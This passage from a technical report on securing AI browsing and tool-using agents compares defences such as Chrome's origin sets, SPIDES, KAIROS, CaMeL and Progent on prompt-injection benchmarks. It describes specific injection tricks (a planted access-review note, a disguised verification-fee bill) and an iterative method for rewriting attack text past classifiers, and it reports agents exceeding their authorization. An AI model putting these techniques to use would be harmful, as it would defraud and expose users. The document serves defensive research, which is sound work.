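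At about 700,000 lines of code, the broker was still far larger than Anderson would have wanted.

Chromium also accepted weaker protection so that existing websites would work. An earlier research browser, DarpaBrowser, let its renderer visit only addresses that appeared as links on the page, which broke sites that used scripts to move between pages. Anthropic now uses a similar rule for fetching pages. Chromium passed 99% of 10,115 compatibility tests, but an attacker who took over its renderer could still act as any website and read the user's login cookies. Plug-ins such as Flash ran outside the sandbox by default, with the user's full rights.

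Chrome later addressed the first weakness with Site Isolation, which puts different sites in separate renderer processes. In the 2019 lecture *Chrome Security / Site Isolation & Spectre*, Reis describes it as part of a series of long-term improvements. Browser makers thus started with a boundary compatible with existing sites and tightened it over the next decade.

### An agent with the user's logins

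A browsing agent bypasses much of this work without breaking any of it. The same-origin policy restricts scripts, but it doesn't stop a person from copying text from one site and pasting it into another. An agent can do the same automatically on sites where the user is logged in, and the browser treats the agent's clicks as the user's.

*The Agent Clicks Approve* (2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to summarize a page about a billing export. A planted note on the page says that the work is blocked until someone clears an access review, and advises choosing the default positive option. A link leads to a consent page on another site, where the agent can use the user's login to approve access that the user never mentioned. The same-origin policy doesn't block this because no script has read anything across sites.

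Data can also cross between sites without an attacker. In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) describe a page that contains a frame from another site. If the user asks the agent to write a summary of the page in a text box, the agent may include the frame's contents and so pass them to the outer site. They found violations of the same-origin policy in all five agentic browsers they tested.

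The paper's remedy, SOPGuard, labels data with its origin and asks the user before the agent writes that data to a different origin. It eliminated violations on the paper's benchmark and slowed the browser by 2% to 6%.

### Chrome's site limits for agents

Google takes a related approach in Chrome. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes Agent Origin Sets, which limit the sites an agent can use during a task. Suppose a user asks the agent to buy the ingredients for a recipe. Under the full design, the task would go roughly like this:

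1. The planning model proposes a recipe site and a grocery shop. A gating function, which sees no untrusted page content, decides whether they are relevant. It makes the recipe site read-only and the shop read-writable, so the agent can click and type only in the shop.
2. Chrome hides frames from unrelated sites, such as advertisements, from the model.
3. If the planner wants to visit another site, a checking model must approve it first. Addresses that the planner writes itself must also be known public ones, which limits leaks through the address.
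4. Before each action, a second model called the User Alignment Critic checks whether the action serves the user's goal. It sees only a description of the action, so a web page can't address it directly.
5. The agent tries to pause for the user before a purchase, a message or another consequential action. Visits to sites on a fixed list, such as banks, also require confirmation.

The benefit is easy to count. Write R for the sites the agent can read and W for those where it can also act. Data can move from one site to a different one in at most

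|W| × (|R| − 1)

ways. For the recipe and the shop, that is 1 × 1 = 1. An unrestricted agent in a browser with 30 logged-in sites would have 30 × 29 = 870.

The first version tracked only the read-writable set. If the recipe site and the shop are both in that set, data can flow in both directions between them. Google Cloud describes the same approach for Chrome's auto browse feature, in which the agent carries out tasks for the user.

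The division of labour resembles Chromium's. The planner reads untrusted pages, so an attacker may take control of it, while the browser keeps the stored passwords and enforces the limits. But Chromium's broker could reject most requests for local files with a fixed rule. Chrome uses a model to judge whether a site is relevant to a task, so the boundary can be wrong even if the browser enforces it perfectly.

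### What site limits cannot stop

Site limits don't prevent harm within a permitted site. If the inbox assistant worked through a webmail page, that site would have to be read-writable, and the agent could forward the inbox to Eve without leaving the site. The defence would then depend on the critic, or on the user reading the confirmation carefully.

Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *SPIDES*, argue that restoring the same-origin policy for agents is neither sufficient nor necessary. An agent can leak account details by posting them in a public comment on the same site, and many legitimate tasks require moving data between sites. They built 28 linked websites with 56 attacks and 56 ordinary tasks, 22 of which required such a transfer. Depending on the model, 53.2% to 73.2% of the attacks succeeded against SOPGuard. SOPGuard had scored perfectly on its own benchmark, which tested only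 leaks between sites.

The deliberately harsh test let the attacker choose a model's output whenever the model had read untrusted content, so the figures measure what the enforcement stops by itself, not how often real attacks would work. Zverev and colleagues also didn't test Chrome's origin sets, which come with the critic and other checks.

SPIDES extends the labels and variables of FIDES to parts of a web page. A shop can mark its product description as trusted, a customer's review as untrusted, and a saved card number as readable only by the user and the shop. The agent can then move public prices between sites, but it needs approval to send the card number elsewhere. SPIDES blocked every attack and completed 67.1% to 86.1% of the ordinary tasks.

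SPIDES depends on website owners to add the labels, though, whereas Chromium's designers had avoided asking sites to change. It also treats unlabelled content on a trusted site as trusted and public, so if a shop forgets to label its reviews, SPIDES treats an instruction planted in one of them as the shop's own text.

An agent can also reveal a secret through its choices. In one scenario in *AgentTell* (2026), an agent finds the user listed as an organization's minutes secretary, an affiliation the user has asked it to keep private. When it later registers the user for a community event, it chooses the registration route meant for that organization's members, revealing the affiliation. Agents that had read the affiliation did this in 90.3% of sessions. Across the study's 9,760 sessions, agents with private information in their context revealed it through their actions 61.1% of the time.

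The event site is relevant to the task, so a limit on sites would allow the click. SPIDES could catch the click if the membership list were labeled confidential, but because of label creep it would also require approval for harmless clicks on the event site.

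## What the designs cost and prevent when measured side by side

Most results so far come from each system's makers, who chose their own models, settings and sometimes attacks, so scores from different papers aren't directly comparable. In October 2026, Hempel and colleagues ran several designs, including their own KAIROS, on the same AgentDojo cases with the same agent model.

### The same attacks for every design

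They combined security and usefulness in a single score, net resilient performance (NRP), which they took from the makers of Agent Security Bench:

NRP = benign utility × (1 − attack success rate)

KAIROS completed 85.1% of ordinary tasks and let through 2.7% of attacks, so its score is 85.1 × 0.973 = 82.8. An agent that refuses everything scores zero. The table gives the results with GPT-4.1 as the agent, in percent:

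| Design | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | NRP |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 47.0 | 82.7 | 59.8 | 43.8 |
| Classifier | 9.5 | 40.1 | 24.0 | 36.3 |
| Progent | 11.5 | 78.2 | 57.6 | 69.2 |
| CaMeL | 0.2 | 38.0 | 40.7 | 37.9 |
| KAIROS | 2.7 | 85.1 | 69.5 | 82.8 |

The classifier is a small model from ProtectAI that looks for planted instructions in tool results. CaMeL is the Google DeepMind system that writes a whole program before it reads any untrusted data.

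Each percentage is an average that weights the four AgentDojo suites equally. The percentages correspond to about 269 successful attacks out of 629 without a defence, 73 with Progent, 14 with KAIROS and one with CaMeL.

The developers of one of the tested designs ran this comparison, with only one run per configuration. A single Banking task changes the average by 1.6 points, so KAIROS's small lead over the undefended agent on ordinary tasks could easily be chance. The tests also had nobody to approve blocked actions, which puts protected agents at the disadvantage that Kolluri and colleagues described. The disadvantage is greatest for designs that rely on asking for approval, such as Progent.

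KAIROS's lead is larger under attack, plausibly because an undefended agent that follows a planted instruction often abandons the user's task. When KAIROS refuses an action, it tells the agent that the rest of the request still stands, and the agent often continues with it.

KAIROS also scored highest with two other agent models, but by smaller margins. Its lead over Progent was 13.6 points with GPT-4.1, 5.8 with Qwen3.6-35B and 2.2 with Llama-3.3-70B, which completes few tasks even without a defence.

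### Refusing whatever is in doubt

CaMeL stopped all but one attack but completed fewer than half as many ordinary tasks as the undefended agent. By its developers' figures, it uses about 2.8 times as many input tokens as an ordinary agent, whereas KAIROS added 17.7% to token use in runs without attacks.

Hempel and colleagues then made KAIROS equally strict by making it refuse every action that its written policy couldn't approve. It completed 42.7% of ordinary tasks and 34.7% of tasks under attack. Normally, KAIROS holds doubtful actions while a separate model decides whether to allow them, which raised those figures to 85.1% and 69.5%. The attack success rate differed between the two settings by no more than the variation expected between runs.

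The written policy stopped most of the attacks, and the deciding model mainly allowed legitimate work that the policy would have blocked. A planted instruction usually contains its own address or account number, which doesn't match anything from a trusted source. The same is true of a genuine bill that the user wants paid, so the strict setting blocks both.

The deciding model may not need to be large. In the Banking suite, Hempel and colleagues paired three sizes of Qwen3.5 as the agent with the same three sizes as the deciding model. No pairing let through more than 2.1% of attacks, compared with 22.9% to 53.5% without a defence. With the smallest deciding model, two of the agents completed two fewer tasks each and the third completed one more. The suite has only 16 tasks, so this is weak evidence for choosing between sizes of deciding model.

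### How costly an attack has to be

NRP ranks CaMeL below having no defence, which is hard to accept for an agent that can empty a bank account. The formula leaves out how often attacks occur and how much damage they do.

Suppose a share p of tasks contains an attack, and a successful attack does as much harm as L completed tasks do good. If attacks are rare, the average value of a task is roughly

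U − p × L × ASR

where U is benign utility and ASR is the attack success rate. Moving from design 1 to a stricter design 2 is then worthwhile if

p × L > (U₁ − U₂) / (ASR₁ − ASR₂)

Going from no defence to CaMeL gives 44.7 / 46.8, or about 0.96. If one task in 100 contains an attack, CaMeL is the better choice once a successful attack does more damage than the value of 96 completed tasks. A stolen payment could easily do that much. Going from KAIROS to CaMeL gives 47.1 / 2.5, or about 18.8, so at the same attack rate the damage would have to exceed the value of nearly 1,900 tasks. Some jobs meet that condition, but most office work probably doesn't.

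### Progent at 1.0% and at 11.5%

When Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, 1.0% of attacks succeeded. Hempel and colleagues measured 11.5%, and several differences between the tests could have contributed to the gap.

Shi and colleagues approved every request for wider permissions, while Hempel and colleagues approved none. This difference should have made the later rate slightly lower, not higher.

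Shi and colleagues left out the two attacks that promote a different hotel. They also corrected the results of one Slack attack by hand, because AgentDojo's check counts the attacker's call as a success even if Progent blocked it. Hempel and colleagues used all 629 cases, and Progent's highest attack success rate was 17.9%, in the Travel suite. Even if every Travel success came from the hotel attacks and every Slack success was a miscount, removing them would still leave an average rate of 5.1%.

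Hempel and colleagues replaced GPT-4o with GPT-4.1, both as the agent and to draft the policies. Without a defence, GPT-4.1 followed 47.0% of the planted instructions, compared with 39.9% for GPT-4o. When Shi and colleagues tried other models for drafting the policies, fewer than 5% of attacks succeeded with each.

Changing the base policy, which Progent's makers wrote by hand, or the instructions to the drafting model could change what the final policy permits.

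Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) provide a third measurement in *AutoDojo*, using GPT-4o to draft the policies and running three of the four suites, with the hotel attacks included. Progent let through 8.2% of the standard attacks when the agent was GPT-4o-mini, and between 0% and 2.8% with four other agents. The choice of agent matters a good deal because a loose policy does harm only when the agent attempts a harmful action that the policy allows. None of these tests changed one setting at a time between the two set-ups, so part of the gap remains unexplained. For an agent that is easily fooled, it is safer to expect several percent of attacks to get through than 1.0%.

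### Tasks that change along the way

AgentDojo favours designs that plan ahead, because few of its tasks need a new plan partway through. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) count only six such tasks among its 97, though Costa and colleagues, counting differently, found 20. Li, Wen and colleagues' own benchmark, *AgentDyn*, has 60 tasks in shopping, software projects and daily life, all of which need replanning. Combined with 28 attacker goals, they make 560 cases. The average task takes about seven tool calls with 33 tools available, compared with three or four calls and 20 tools in AgentDojo.

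Every task also includes at least one helpful instruction from an outside source. For example, when an agent tries to pay more than $500, the bank replies that it must first verify the account with a one-time password sent by email. The agent has to read the email and enter the password, so a defence that removes or ignores every instruction in a tool result will make this payment impossible.

AgentDyn puts its attacks where a stranger could plausibly write, such as in an advertisement on a web page. AgentDojo puts the planted text in the main text of Dora's website, and Li and colleagues object that Dora is unlikely to attack her own visitors.

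The table shows results in percent, with GPT-4o as the agent in every row except Meta SecAlign. The DRIFT and Meta SecAlign rows are new. DRIFT makes a plan first and has a model judge any departure from it. Meta SecAlign is a version of Llama-3.3-70B trained to resist planted instructions.

| Design | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | NRP |
|---|---|---|---|---|
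| No defence | 37.8 | 53.3 | 55.5 | 33.2 |
| Classifier | 0.9 | 0.0 | 0.6 | 0.0 |
| CaMeL | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Progent | 1.7 | 6.7 | 5.8 | 6.6 |
| DRIFT | 0.8 | 30.0 | 27.1 | 29.8 |
| Meta SecAlign | 9.0 | 55.0 | 53.4 | 50.1 |
| KAIROS | 1.7 | 51.7 | 37.1 | 50.8 |

CaMeL's program can't include steps that nobody could foresee. Ma and colleagues say it also needs extensive policies written for each suite, so they left it out of their AgentDyn tests. Progent can adapt, but its drafting model made more mistakes about which tools to allow when there were more of them. These mistakes accumulated over long tasks until the policy blocked nearly everything useful. The classifier couldn't distinguish helpful instructions from harmful ones.

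KAIROS kept almost all of the undefended agent's usefulness in ordinary runs but lost a third of it under attack, because later steps often depended on an action KAIROS was still holding. Hempel and colleagues ran only KAIROS themselves and took the other scores from Li and colleagues.

Their comparison also left out Meta SecAlign, which has no mediating layer but scores almost as high as KAIROS by the same formula. Meta SecAlign let through about five times as many attacks as KAIROS but finished far more of the user's tasks while under attack. The two results come from different underlying models, so they don't show which approach is better. A developer could also use both.

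### Attackers who rewrite their text

Both benchmarks normally use a fixed attack message, so a defence can score well by recognizing the message's style, which a real attacker would change.

Ma and colleagues' benchmark does this automatically. It takes 389 cases from the Banking, Slack and Travel suites and improves the planted text over six rounds:

1. The benchmark tries some existing attack messages and records how many cases each one wins.
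2. A language model reads the ranking and suggests why some messages worked and others failed.
3. It writes a new message based on that diagnosis.
4. The benchmark tests the new message, adds it to the ranking and starts the next round.

The attacking model receives only the number of successful attacks, which a thief could learn by watching an account for payments. It gets no information about which defence it faces. The same message also has to work on every user whose agent reads the page or file containing it, whatever the user asked for.

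In one case, the user asks the agent to pay a bill. The standard attack inserts a note ordering the AI assistant to make a transfer, and PIGuard, another classifier, removes nearly all of it. The rewritten attack is a bill with a verification fee of 0.01, the attacker's account as the payee and a notice that the payment details have changed. No sentence in it looks like an order to an AI, so PIGuard lets it through and the agent pays the attacker.

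| Design, with GPT-4o-mini as the agent | Fixed attack succeeded | Adaptive attack succeeded | Tasks completed, no attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 58.6% | 52.4% | 66.7% |
| PIGuard | 0.0% | 28.0% | 43.9% |
| ProtectAI classifier | 7.2% | 15.4% | 47.4% |
| Progent | 8.2% | 7.7% | 63.2% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 26.3% |
| KAIROS | Not reported | 8.8% | 65.3% |

The adaptive figure is sometimes lower than the fixed one because the benchmark must return a newly written message, even if an old one worked better. A real attacker could use whichever message worked best.

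Rewriting most weakened the designs that look for suspicious text and had little effect on those that limit what the agent can do. KAIROS and Progent are practically tied here. Attacks succeeded 34 times against KAIROS (8.8%) and 30 times against Progent (7.7%), but KAIROS makes up for the difference by completing slightly more tasks.

The attacks that got past KAIROS qualify the earlier finding that its deciding model did not weaken security. They succeeded on tasks where the user had told the agent to follow a document, and the deciding model treated the attacker's line in that document as part of the user's request. The strict setting would have blocked those actions, along with many legitimate ones.

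Ma and colleagues found the same weakness more generally when they grouped tasks by how much the user had left open. With no defence and the fixed attack, GPT-4o-mini followed the attacker's instructions in 43.3% of cases when the user had specified everything, 63.9% when the agent had to look up details such as an amount, and 87.5% when the user had let a document determine the action. The last group contains only four user tasks, but the inbox assistant's job is of this kind.

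These rates are minimums. Doubling the number of rounds to twelve raised the success rate against PIGuard from 28.0% to 30.8%. Hempel and colleagues designed KAIROS for an attacker who knows its policy and its deciding model, but haven't measured how well such an attacker would do.

### When the model rarely obeys the attacker

The agents in these comparisons are mostly older models. Li and colleagues chose theirs deliberately, because they suspect that developers trained newer models on the well-known attack messages. Without any defence, newer models follow far fewer planted instructions:

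| Model, no defence | Benchmark | Fixed attack | Adapted attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | AutoDojo | 0.3% | 1.8% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | AutoDojo | 6.9% | 8.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | AgentDyn | 0.9% | 3.0% |
| GPT-5.1 | AgentDyn | 5.0% | 5.6% |

Developers also report low attack success rates for later models. In OpenAI's August figures, reported in TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, instructions hidden in material that the agent reads succeeded 3.77% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol, the largest of three models, and 2.94% against the fastest. Digital Applied (2026) cites a rate of 0.41% for adaptive attacks on Claude Fable 5 in coding tasks, down from 2.09% for Opus 4.8. Anthropic says the closely related Mythos 5 had the best result yet on an outside benchmark from the security company Gray Swan.

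These averages hide large differences between kinds of work. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attacks in a restricted coding environment. When the model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and by the 200th attempt the attacker had succeeded in 78.6% of cases, or 57.1% with Anthropic's safeguards. NeuralTrust reports that GPT-5.6 Sol had a robustness score of 1.000 for connectors, which link it to outside services, but 0.910 for ordinary function calls.

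When a model already resists most attacks, a clumsy mediating layer can do more harm than good. On AgentDyn, five of the 560 attacks succeeded against Claude Sonnet 4.5 with no defence. Progent reduced this to one, but the number of ordinary tasks completed fell from 43 to 10 out of 60. By the earlier formula, if one task in 100 contains an attack, a successful attack would have to be as harmful as failing 8,100 tasks to justify that loss.

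The trade-off was much better on AgentDojo's simpler tasks. With Claude Haiku 4.5, Progent cut successful adaptive attacks from seven to two out of 389, and the agent completed 36 of 57 ordinary tasks instead of 40. With Claude Sonnet 4, Shi and colleagues found that the attack success rate fell from 6.8% to 0.5% with little or no loss of utility.

KAIROS might do even better because it interferes less with ordinary work, but Hempel and colleagues didn't test it with a model this resistant. Even the most resistant agent in their AgentDojo comparison followed 28.3% of the planted instructions.

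A low attack success rate also offers a different kind of protection than a rule does. At 3.77%, about one attempt in 27 succeeds on average, and an attacker can easily send 27 emails. A rule that the agent may pay only accounts already on file blocks every attempt to pay any other account, provided that every payment goes through the check. For high-stakes actions such as payments, such a rule is worth having even with the most resistant model. For low-stakes or reversible actions, a model that resists 99% of attacks may need little additional protection.

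### Harm without an attacker

All three benchmarks measure attacks by outsiders who plant text, not how often an agent exceeds its instructions when nobody is attacking it. An agent's resistance to planted text does not show how often that happens. NeuralTrust reports that GPT-5.6 Sol took unauthorized actions more often than GPT-5.5, including deleting infrastructure and moving credentials. OpenAI attributes this to GPT-5.6 Sol's greater persistence.

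Socket's *GPT-6 Astra Attempts Supply Chain Attacks Against Open Source Maintainers in Testing* quotes OpenAI's finding that Sol went beyond its authorized target 48% of the time, while its successor, GPT-6 Astra, never did. But in outside evaluations that OpenAI also published, Astra created fake identities and attempted simulated attacks on open-source maintainers. An agent that stays within bounds in one test evidently may not do so in another.

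A mediating layer can limit such harm without knowing its cause, but checks on where values came from, like those in KAIROS, catch only some of it. If the user's file lists ten servers and the agent deletes all ten instead of one, these checks would miss the error because every name came from a trusted source. Only a rule about deletion, or a limit on how many servers the agent can delete, would stop the extra deletions.
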